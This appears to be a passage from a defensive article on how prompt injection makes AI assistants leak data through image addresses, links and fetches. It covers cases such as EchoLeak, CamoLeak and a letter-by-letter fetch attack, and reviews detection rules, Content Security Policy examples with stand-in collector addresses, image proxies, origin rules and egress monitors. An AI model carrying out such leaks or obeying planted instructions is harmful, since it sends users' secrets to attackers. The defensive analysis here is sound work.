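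ThaiCERT's advice about Bing has lasted better. ReLeak's image attack also went through Bing, but it started with an email, so a search for suspicious links would not have found it. But ThaiCERT did not define "abnormal", so an administrator would need something like the Bing rule above to act on the advice.

NopalCyber's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise* (2026) offers more specific rules. One flags search links that contain HTML tags or the codes for angle brackets and quotation marks. People use quotation marks to search for an exact phrase, so that part will cause false alarms. Another rule looks for the image file name from Varonis's demonstration, which an attacker could change. The advisory also suggests searching WAF and server logs for the final request to the attacker, but Bing sends that request, so it would not appear in the victim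 company's logs.

Echelon Risk + Cyber, a security consultancy, published searches for companies without full web addresses in their logs. Its main rule alerts when a computer looks up Copilot's host name and then connects to an address outside Microsoft within 60 seconds. The firm calls this rule "High Fidelity", but it has two problems:

- In SearchLeak, the victim's browser sent the data to Bing, which Microsoft owns, so the rule would probably have missed the attack it was written for.
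- An office browser with several tabs open contacts other companies all the time, so the rule needs a long list of exclusions.

A second Echelon rule requires at least five Bing image lookups within two minutes. SearchLeak could steal a login code with one.

Other published rules work on text inside the application. Datadog's *Data exfiltration successful* alerts when the company's AI filter classifies something as data theft but doesn't block it, with the highest severity if the data includes personal information or credentials. "Successful" means only that the filter let it through, so the alert doesn't show that the data reached an attacker. The rule's instructions are to block the attacking network address, but in an indirect injection that address could be the employee's own.

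trackr.live also points to an experimental rule for image links from Agent Threat Rules, an open collection of patterns for attacks on AI agents. The rule's own documentation acknowledges that HTML image tags can bypass it. Help Net Security's *Agent Threat Rules* reports that the collection caught 98.0 percent of the hostile prompts in one public test set and none in two others, although every rule had passed its own tests. Those sets did not test image leaks specifically, but the spread shows why a company should test published rules on new wordings and addresses before relying on them.

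### Measured detection rates

Nobody appears to have published detection and false alarm rates for image leaks from AI assistants in real office traffic. The advice to prefer destinations over randomness, the expected number of alerts and the choice of time windows all rest on practitioners' judgement. Researchers have measured detectors for related kinds of traffic, which gives some idea of what to expect.

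The closest work to detecting this leak is a detector for malicious tools. In *ShieldNet*, Yuan, Chen and colleagues (2026) added hidden code to tools that AI agents use through the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to outside services. Their detector read the decrypted traffic from each tool run, found nearly all the malicious runs and wrongly flagged 0.8 percent of the harmless ones. General-purpose models, including GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5, wrongly flagged 26.5 to 34.4 percent of harmless tools when they read the same kind of traffic.

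These results don't transfer directly to image leaks, where the software works as designed and the model writes the address. The hidden code also ran every time an agent used the tool, and the researchers left delayed or slow attacks for later work. If a detector for image requests had the same 0.8 percent false alarm rate, 100,000 requests a day would produce 800 false alerts. The earlier calculation used a rate of one in 100,000, which is 800 times lower, and no published result shows that a SOC can achieve it.

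A detector can also score well in a test despite a high false alarm rate. *Detecting Data Exfiltration through I2P Anonymity Networks* (2026) tested models for separating theft from ordinary browsing on I2P, a network that hides its users' identities. The best model caught 2,339 of 2,519 thefts, or 92.85 percent, and wrongly flagged 150 browsing sessions, or 12.57 percent. About 94 percent of its alerts were real because two-thirds of the test traffic was theft. At the same rates, five thefts among 100,000 image requests would produce about 12,570 false alerts, and fewer than one alert in 2,000 would be real.

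The choice of model can matter just as much. *Evasion-Resilient Detection of DNS-over-HTTPS Data Exfiltration* (2025) tested several detectors on data hidden in encrypted DNS lookups. Two standard machine learning methods caught 99 to 100 percent of the traffic in each scenario, while a third caught 0 to 7 percent. Some scenarios contained only one connection, so the perfect scores are weak evidence.

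### Decryption and the second copy of the secret

Without decryption, the SOC could not have told the assistant's five requests from the news site's in the invented log, so `ads.example` and `pictures.example` would have looked equally suspicious. Requests 5 and 6 would have looked like normal visits to approved services.

To decrypt traffic, the company has to install its own certificate on every device, which also lets it read employees' other browsing unless it makes exceptions. Some programs can avoid the gateway by using QUIC, a newer protocol for web traffic. Yuan and colleagues blocked QUIC so that programs such as Claude's desktop app could not bypass their proxy. A company would need to block QUIC too or use a gateway that can inspect it.

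Decryption also puts secrets, such as the login code in request 5, into the logs. The decoder makes this worse by turning hidden values into readable text, and the alert may copy that text into a ticket, an email and a chat message. If an AI assistant can read any of those, the stolen data is back in a model's context, along with an address the attacker wrote.

trackr.live recommends running the decoder and the DLP search in an isolated system and, where possible, sending the SIEM only the result or a hash. An ordinary hash does not protect a six-digit code, because there are only a million possibilities and a computer can try them all almost instantly. An HMAC, the keyed code that Camo uses for its signatures, prevents this as long as the key stays out of the log system. Analysts can still see that two alerts involve the same value without seeing the value itself.

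## Checking and blocking image addresses inside the application

The application can act before any image loads, because the model's answer passes through the developer's code first. A gateway can only log a request after the browser has sent it.

### Removing external images

The simplest control is to display no images from outside hosts. In 2024, GitHub stopped Copilot Chat in the Visual Studio Code editor from loading Markdown images from untrusted domains, according to Willison. After CamoLeak, GitHub disabled all images in Copilot Chat on its website, according to Legit Security.

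Google's Gemini uses a sanitizer, a program that removes unsafe parts of the model's output before the user sees it. The sanitizer stops images with outside addresses from loading. It is one of several layers of defense (The Hacker News, 2025). Google also removes links that its Safe Browsing service lists as malicious and asks users to confirm risky actions.

A developer can build a similar filter in four steps:

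1. Parse the answer with the same parser that the renderer uses.
2. Keep only a short list of element types, such as paragraphs, headings, lists and tables.
3. Replace each image with its caption.
4. Build the page from what remains.

The shared parser matters because EchoLeak got past Microsoft's filter with an image notation that only the renderer recognised. Listing what to keep is safer than listing what to remove, because unfamiliar notation then ends up as plain text. If the application accepts HTML or diagrams, the same steps have to cover them.

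Blocking outside images has little effect on an inbox assistant, because its summaries rarely need pictures. It affects an assistant that makes charts more if the assistant relies on an outside chart service. The developer can instead have the browser draw the chart from the numbers in the answer, which needs no outside request.

Other content, such as fonts, can also load automatically. According to daily.dev's summary of a conference talk, a researcher used CVE-2026-24299, a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot assistants, to get data out through the address of a font in an HTML preview. Microsoft patched the flaw in early 2026. A filter that removed only images would have missed this, so the list of permitted elements should exclude styles too.

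Removing images also doesn't stop link previews in messaging apps. PromptArmor found that the agent OpenClaw was exposed to data leaks through these previews by default on Telegram. Some messaging services let a bot turn off previews for its own messages, which prevents these leaks without removing the links.

A tester has to record network traffic to check whether the application blocks image requests, as with leaks through tool calls. In a demonstration by the security company Checkmarx, no picture appeared in the chat, but the request reached the researchers' server.

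### Cleaning the answer before anyone sees it

SearchLeak showed that a correct filter can run too late. Copilot displayed its answer while the model was still writing it, before the filter ran. The safest fix is to wait for the complete answer, filter it and then show it. At 50 tokens a second, the user would wait 10 seconds for a 500-token answer.

A developer can avoid most of that delay by holding back only the parts that might become an image. The application shows ordinary words immediately, as plain text. When it reaches a character that could begin an image, it waits until the notation is complete, checks the address and then either creates the image or shows the caption. If the image takes 40 tokens, the pause is less than a second:

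40 tokens ÷ 50 tokens per second = 0.8 seconds

The application has to wait longer to check an image written in the footnote-style notation from EchoLeak, because the address may come at the very end of the answer. Until then, the application can display the caption as text.

The cleaning code can also cause the leak. A browser may start loading an image as soon as a script sets the image's address, even if the image is not yet on the page. Code that puts raw HTML into an ordinary page element and then deletes the image tags may trigger the request it was supposed to prevent. Browsers can also parse HTML in a separate kind of document that loads nothing, and the cleaning code should use that.

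Every program that displays the answer needs the same protection. Cleaning the answer on the server protects both the website and the mobile app, provided that neither later turns the cleaned text back into images. trackr.live advises developers to trace the output to everything that might use it, including code editors, log viewers and ticketing systems. A team whose API returns only raw text may not realize that a customer's ticketing system loads the images linked in that text.

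### Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy lets the browser block images that the cleaning code misses. Microsoft fixed Bing Chat in May 2023 with a policy that generally blocked image loading, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

A simplified policy for the company's assistant might look like this:

`Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none'; img-src https://files.example/public/ https://preview.trusted.example`

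The `img-src` part lists the permitted image sources. The `default-src 'none'` part blocks other content that has no rule of its own, including fonts. A real page would also need rules for its scripts and styles.

The first entry includes a path, so it permits only addresses under `/public/` on that host. After each redirect, the browser still checks the host but not the path. If it also checked the path, a site could learn where a redirect led on another site by testing which paths the browser blocked. The table shows how the policy treats several invented addresses.

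| Image address | Requested directly | Reached by redirect from an approved address |
|---|---|---|
| `https://files.example/public/photo.png` | Allowed | Allowed |
| `https://files.example/forms/submit?text=INVENTED-VALUE` | Blocked | Allowed |
| `https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=INVENTED-VALUE` | Blocked | Blocked |
| `https://preview.trusted.example/fetch?url=https://collector.example/INVENTED-VALUE` | Allowed | Allowed |

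The second row resembles the Superhuman case, where a form was on the same host as ordinary documents. Adding a path to the policy would block the form unless the attacker found an approved address that redirects to it. trackr.live therefore recommends restricting redirects and checking who owns the account or storage space behind an approved address, instead of relying on the path alone.

The last row is a relay, which contacts `collector.example` from its own server, where the browser's policy has no effect. The policy also does not cover other requests that start on a server, or mobile and desktop apps that load images without a browser component. It does not stop a user from following a link.

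#### Report-only mode

A strict policy can break an application if the developer forgot to list a legitimate image source. Browsers therefore support a trial version, which the server sends in a header called `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only`. The browser loads everything as usual but sends a report whenever the policy would have blocked something.

trackr.live suggests starting with a tight image list and running it long enough to include unusual work, such as a quarterly report. The developer then examines each reported host and adds the ones the application needs. The reports have some gaps:

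- Not every browser delivers them reliably.
- For images on other sites, the report gives only the site and leaves out the rest of the address. This keeps stolen data out of the reports, but an analyst can't use them to find out what was stolen.
- An attacker can cause false reports, so a script should not add reported hosts to the allowlist automatically.
- A relay's request to the attacker never appears, because the browser did not make it.

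Report-only mode also blocks nothing, so an image request carrying the colleague's access key would still reach the attacker. If the assistant reads private data, the developer should keep external images off during the trial.

### Image proxies

An image proxy, such as GitHub's Camo, fetches external images for the browser, so the browser's content security policy needs to allow images only from the proxy. The server hosting the image also receives the proxy's IP address instead of the user's.

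A proxy that fetches any address it receives does not stop the theft. Suppose the model writes an address containing the colleague's key. The application rewrites the address to go through the proxy, the browser asks for the picture, and the proxy requests the original address, with the key still in it, from the attacker's server. The attacker gets the same log entry as before, and the company's gateway now records only a visit to the assistant's own host.

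Signing image addresses helps only if the application chooses which ones to sign before the model writes anything. An application that signs every image address in a finished answer would also sign the one containing the key. Even signing addresses in advance did not stop CamoLeak, because the attack encoded the secret in the order of the requests.

A developer could close that gap by fetching the pictures earlier:

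1. The application retrieves an email or document.
2. It fetches every picture in it and stores a copy.
3. Only then does it give the text to the model.
4. If the answer includes one of those pictures, the browser loads the stored copy.

The proxy requests the pictures from outside servers before the model reads anything, so private data cannot affect the contents or order of these requests. In a CamoLeak attack, the attacker's server would receive only one request for each prepared picture. This design uses storage and fetches many pictures that nobody will view. Senders also learn that the assistant has retrieved their email, as they would with a tracking pixel. The protection lasts only if the proxy never fetches a picture again from the original server when the browser requests it.

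### The origin rule

An application whose assistant has to open web pages can't practically block all outside addresses, but it can check where each address came from. Under an origin rule, the assistant may fetch an address that the user typed or that a trusted step, such as a web search, returned, but never one the model composed. An attacker can still plant text that tells the model to add the colleague's key to an address, but the application refuses the resulting address because it appears only in the model's output.

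Anthropic built its web fetch tool for Claude this way. The developer documentation, *Web fetch tool*, states that Claude "is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs". The tool accepts addresses from the user's messages, from tools that the developer runs, and from earlier searches and fetches. It rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. Anthropic warns that some risk remains when untrusted text and sensitive data share a context, and suggests turning the tool off, limiting the number of fetches, or restricting it to known safe domains.

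The rule checks for an exact text match between an image's origin and a list of trusted origins, so the application doesn't have to recognise a secret or judge a site's reputation. An attacker can't change the result with persuasive wording. But the protection depends on which origins are on the list.

#### The gap Ayush Paul found

The consumer version of Claude followed a similar rule but could also open links on pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul's letter-by-letter attack used only such links, so opening them did not break the rule. Willison (2026) reports that Paul extracted a name and the user's home city and employer from Claude's memory of past conversations.

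The planted text gave Claude a plausible reason to follow the letters, which was to find the user's profile. Paul's site showed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would have seen something else.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and it did not pay a reward. The fix stops the tool from following links in fetched pages, so Claude can no longer browse a site from page to page unless a search returns each address or the user supplies it.

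As with CamoLeak, the size of the leak depends on the number of addresses available. With 36 links, for the letters and digits, each choice carries log₂ 36 bits:

log₂ 36 ≈ 5.17 bits per fetch

5 fetches × 5.17 bits ≈ 26 bits

A limit of five fetches would therefore let an attacker steal five letters of a name. Stealing the colleague's 40-character key, at 6 bits per character, would take 47 fetches. An attacker who offers 1,000 links on each page gets about 10 bits per fetch, so could steal about 50 bits under the same limit. Limiting fetches works well to protect documents and long keys but poorly to protect a short fact, such as a city.

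#### Settings for developers

Developers who use Claude through Anthropic's API should check their `url_sources` setting. According to a newer version of Anthropic's documentation, with examples that use Claude Opus 5.5, the fetch tool still accepts addresses from earlier fetches by default. Developers can use the setting to exclude those addresses, which brings the tool close to the consumer app's fixed behaviour.

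The same setting can exclude tools that repeat the model's own text. If Claude writes a program that prints an address and the developer's tool returns the output, the address appears in a tool result and so meets the rule. Error messages that quote Claude's input can have the same effect. The documentation recommends excluding such tools by name, or excluding all of the developer's tools.

The newer tool also refuses addresses that seem to contain a password or access key, unless the same value appears in the developer's instructions or the text of a user message. It therefore still refuses an address containing a key that appeared only in a tool result. This would protect the colleague's key if the employee's assistant received her email as a tool result, but the check would miss a contract price, which doesn't look like a password or key.

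In this interface, the "user message" can contain text that didn't come from the user. In a 2025 post, Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted content into that message. If the employee's assistant does this with her email, every address the stranger wrote counts as one she supplied. The stranger could then repeat Paul's attack with a list of 36 prepared addresses and no page of links. A developer can avoid this by returning emails as tool results and excluding those results as a source of addresses.

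The rule covers only the fetch tool. A program in a code sandbox can make its own requests if the sandbox has internet access, as in ReLeak's third attack. Anthropic's desktop agent, Claude Cowork, limited such requests to a list of domains, but the list included Anthropic's API. In January 2026, Willison reported that PromptArmor had got the agent to upload a user's files there using the attacker's API key, which let the attacker download them. The domain was trustworthy, but anyone could open an account on it, so a safer check would also have required uploads to go to the user's own account.

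#### OpenAI's public index

OpenAI checks the origin of an address differently. *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a crawler that records public web addresses in an index, without access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT can automatically load an address that is already in the index. An address containing the colleague's key would not be in the index, because nobody had published it.

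If an address is unknown, ChatGPT either looks for another source or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation. The warning can show exactly what the request would send. OpenAI calls the system Safe Url and also uses it in its Atlas browser and for searches in Deep Research, its tool for longer investigations.

OpenAI chose the index over a list of trusted sites for two reasons. Trusted sites often have redirects, so checking only the first domain is not enough, and a short list would produce so many warnings that people would learn to click through them. The index avoids warnings on ordinary public pages, but it can't include private pictures in a company's document store. An assistant that works mainly with internal files would therefore still produce many warnings.

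Rehberger considers the system a significant improvement but notes that an attacker can again use one public page per letter. Many blogs already have 36 indexed pages. OpenAI's own paper acknowledges this. He suggests that an agent should not request the same address twice in a session, or should reuse a stored copy. The most that 36 pages could then convey, if the agent visited each one once, is:

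log₂ 36! ≈ 138 bits

That is too little for the 240-bit key. A site with 1,000 indexed pages could still receive the key in 25 visits to different pages, so limiting total visits to a site would help more. Requests may also arrive in a different order than the model intended, which makes the attack harder.

Rehberger also worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check or may forget to use it. The check was previously missing from OpenAI's mobile and macOS apps. In May 2026, Permiso Security found that ChatGPT loaded images from a page it had summarised. This could be another example, although addresses on a public page might already have been in the index.

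### Tracking where data came from

An origin rule checks web addresses. Some researchers have built systems that instead track every value an agent handles. The application can then refuse to send private data to an outsider, whatever form the request takes.

The best-known is CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues (2025) presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. It separates planning from reading. If the employee asks for a summary of her unread email, it works like this:

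1. One model reads only her request and writes a short program to fetch the emails, summarise them and show the result.
2. A second model, which has no tools, reads the emails and writes the summary.
3. An interpreter runs the program and labels each value with its sources and the people allowed to read it.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter compares the labels with the developer's rules.

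The planning model never reads the stranger's email, so the email can't add a step to the program, though it can still distort the summary. If a later step would send text from the colleague's email to an unknown address, the interpreter could block that step or ask the employee.

The team tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a set of simulated tasks involving email, banking, travel and workplace chat. CaMeL completed 77 percent of the tasks with its security guarantees in place, compared with 84 percent for an undefended system.

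Some of the lost tasks are ones people would want an assistant to do, such as carrying out whatever a colleague requested in an email. The planning model can't write a program for that without reading the email, and letting it read email would give a stranger's message the same influence. Developers also have to write the rules, and users have to answer questions when a rule blocks something legitimate.

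CaMeL would not automatically stop an image leak. In the employee's case, the second model reads both the colleague's key and the stranger's instructions, so it could put the key into an image address within the summary. The program then displays the summary, as she asked. To prevent the leak, the developer has to bring the renderer into the protected system by treating loading an image as a tool call with a recipient and applying the rules to it.

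*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa et al., 2025) describes Fides, a related system developed at Microsoft. Fides labels data by how confidential it is and how trustworthy its source is, and can hide untrusted text from the planning model until a step needs it. It completed a broad range of tasks on the AgentDojo benchmark while enforcing its rules, but it still depends on correct labels and on a rule for every channel through which data can leave.

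In *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, Metere (2026) doubts that labels can work for language models, because data comes out "transformed in ways no taint engine can follow". This is a good objection to tracking individual words through a model, but CaMeL avoids the problem by giving the second model's whole output the labels of everything that model read. This is safe but coarse, since one confidential email can make an entire summary too sensitive to send.

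Small leaks can remain even with correct labels. If a program contacts an outside site once for each item on a private list, the number of requests reveals the length of the list. The CaMeL paper acknowledges such side channels.

### An egress monitor that measures leftover capacity

Metere's own approach, published in May 2026, assumes that an attacker already controls the agent and that the destination is approved. His monitor inspects each outgoing message and tries to destroy any data hidden in it, for example in invisible characters, extra spaces or the choice between synonyms. It removes or standardises these features before sending the message.

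For encoded text, it keeps a budget for each destination. It counts each Base64 character as up to 6 bits, so the colleague's encoded key would cost:

54 characters × 6 bits = 324 bits

Once a destination has used its budget, the monitor can delay or cancel further suspicious messages. Because the budget refills over time, this limits how fast data can leak but not the total amount.

#### How Metere tested it

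Metere wrote fifteen programs that hide data in text, images or sound, each with a matching program to recover it. For the text tests, he sent random secrets through the monitor in 20 trials per method and setting. He then calculated how much information the recovered bits, Y, gave about the hidden bits, X:

I(X;Y) = Σ p(x,y) × log₂ [p(x,y) ÷ (p(x) × p(y))]

The result is 1 bit for each hidden bit if zeros and ones are equally common and the receiver recovers every bit correctly, and 0 if the receiver can only guess. Metere also applied a standard correction because small samples slightly inflate the result.

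With every protection turned on, the measured capacity fell to zero for all the text methods. With the default setting, Metere reports an average reduction of only 60.2 percent. That setting stopped invisible characters and lookalike letters, but data hidden in spaces, punctuation, synonyms and Base64 got through completely. The monitor recorded a warning each time but left the message unchanged, because Metere wanted to avoid damaging legitimate text in a new installation.

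One image method kept some capacity even with the protection on. An agent can signal through the overall brightness of each picture it sends, and the monitor can't remove that without ruining the pictures. It rounds the brightness to one of eight levels, which leaves at most:

log₂ 8 = 3 bits per image

The paper also accepts that an agent can always convey one bit by sending a message or staying silent.

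#### What the zeros mean

A measured capacity of zero applies only to the encoder and decoder tested. An attacker who knows how the monitor works could design a different method, and the test sets no upper limit on how much data that method might leak. Metere presents the fifteen programs as a starting set and invites others to add more. He also tested his own company's product, so an independent test with new encoders would be more convincing.

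None of the fifteen methods put data in an image address. The monitor might stop the encoded key if its Base64 checks were set to block, but a readable email title in an address would use little or none of the budget. The monitor's filters work on message text, and Metere notes that interactive elements and some message metadata need separate checks.

One part of the design is close to CamoLeak. If an agent sends several image files, their order can carry data. Four different images have 24 possible orders:

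log₂ 4! ≈ 4.6 bits

The monitor sorts unsigned images by a hash of their contents, so the agent no longer controls the order. This works for files the agent sends, but CamoLeak used image addresses that the victim's browser loaded. Sorting those addresses would not be enough, because the attacker would still learn which letters the secret contained and how often each appeared.

For an inbox assistant, removing images takes less effort than any of this and stops the leak more reliably. A monitor like Metere's makes more sense where an agent has to send messages to outsiders and the company worries about hidden data in them.

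### The dispute between Checkmarx, Microsoft and Google

Developers will add these controls only if their company considers the leak its problem. In October 2025, Checkmarx researchers reported related leaks to Microsoft and Google, and they published the companies' differing answers in *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*.

Checkmarx's report to Microsoft, submitted on 15 October, concerned Copilot Chat in a developer's working environment. If the assistant read an article controlled by an attacker, text planted in the article could make it put an access key into an image address, and the image request would send the key out without the user clicking anything. Microsoft said on 28 October that its engineers were still working on the report, then closed it on 4 November without a fix.

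Microsoft gave several reasons for not classing the behaviour as a vulnerability:

- The attack needed "multiple non-default user actions".
- It did not work reliably in different environments.
- The product displayed warnings intended to reduce the risk.
- Users are expected to review and trust the code they choose to run, a principle the reply called "Workplace Trust".

It passed the report to its engineers so they could look for ways to make the behaviour clearer to users. The last reason resembles the idea behind Workspace Trust, a Visual Studio Code feature that asks whether the user trusts a project's files. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename* reports that the vendor similarly declined to release a fix for another flaw in 2025 because it considered Workspace Trust sufficient.

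This argument is reasonable for code in a project the user chose to open, but weaker for an online article, because trusting a project doesn't mean trusting every page the assistant reads while working on it. Microsoft's first two reasons are harder to judge, since Checkmarx doesn't list the user actions or say how often the attack worked. If the user had to approve several unusual steps, the attack was much less dangerous than EchoLeak, which needed no such approval.

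Microsoft's position is also hard to reconcile with its other decisions. Microsoft (2025) says indirect prompt injection can lead to theft of the user's data, and the company fixed EchoLeak and SearchLeak. GitHub, which Microsoft owns, had blocked images from untrusted domains in Copilot Chat for Visual Studio Code the year before Checkmarx's report. Microsoft didn't explain in its reply how the case Checkmarx reported differed from the one in Copilot Chat.

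Gemini's sanitizer already blocked the equivalent image leak, but Gemini could still write an ordinary link containing private data, and clicking it would send the data to the attacker. Checkmarx reported this to Google on 5 October. Google's Safe Browsing check removes links to sites already known to be malicious, but an attacker can avoid it by registering a new domain.

Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". In its written reply, it instead said that the issue was not severe enough to track as a security bug and fell outside its reward programme. Both reasons may be true, since an assistant that searches the web has to show links, and users can at least inspect an address before clicking. But few people read a long address closely, and Checkmarx argues that Google should warn users if it leaves this risk to them.

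Google has not been consistent across products either, and has described image loading in its Antigravity coding tool as intended behaviour. At both companies, the decision seems to depend partly on the product. Coding tools rely on developers to judge what they open, while an office assistant reads whatever arrives in the mailbox. But a developer who approves a web page cannot practically foresee an image request that the assistant will write a minute later. The company that makes the renderer can block such requests for everyone.
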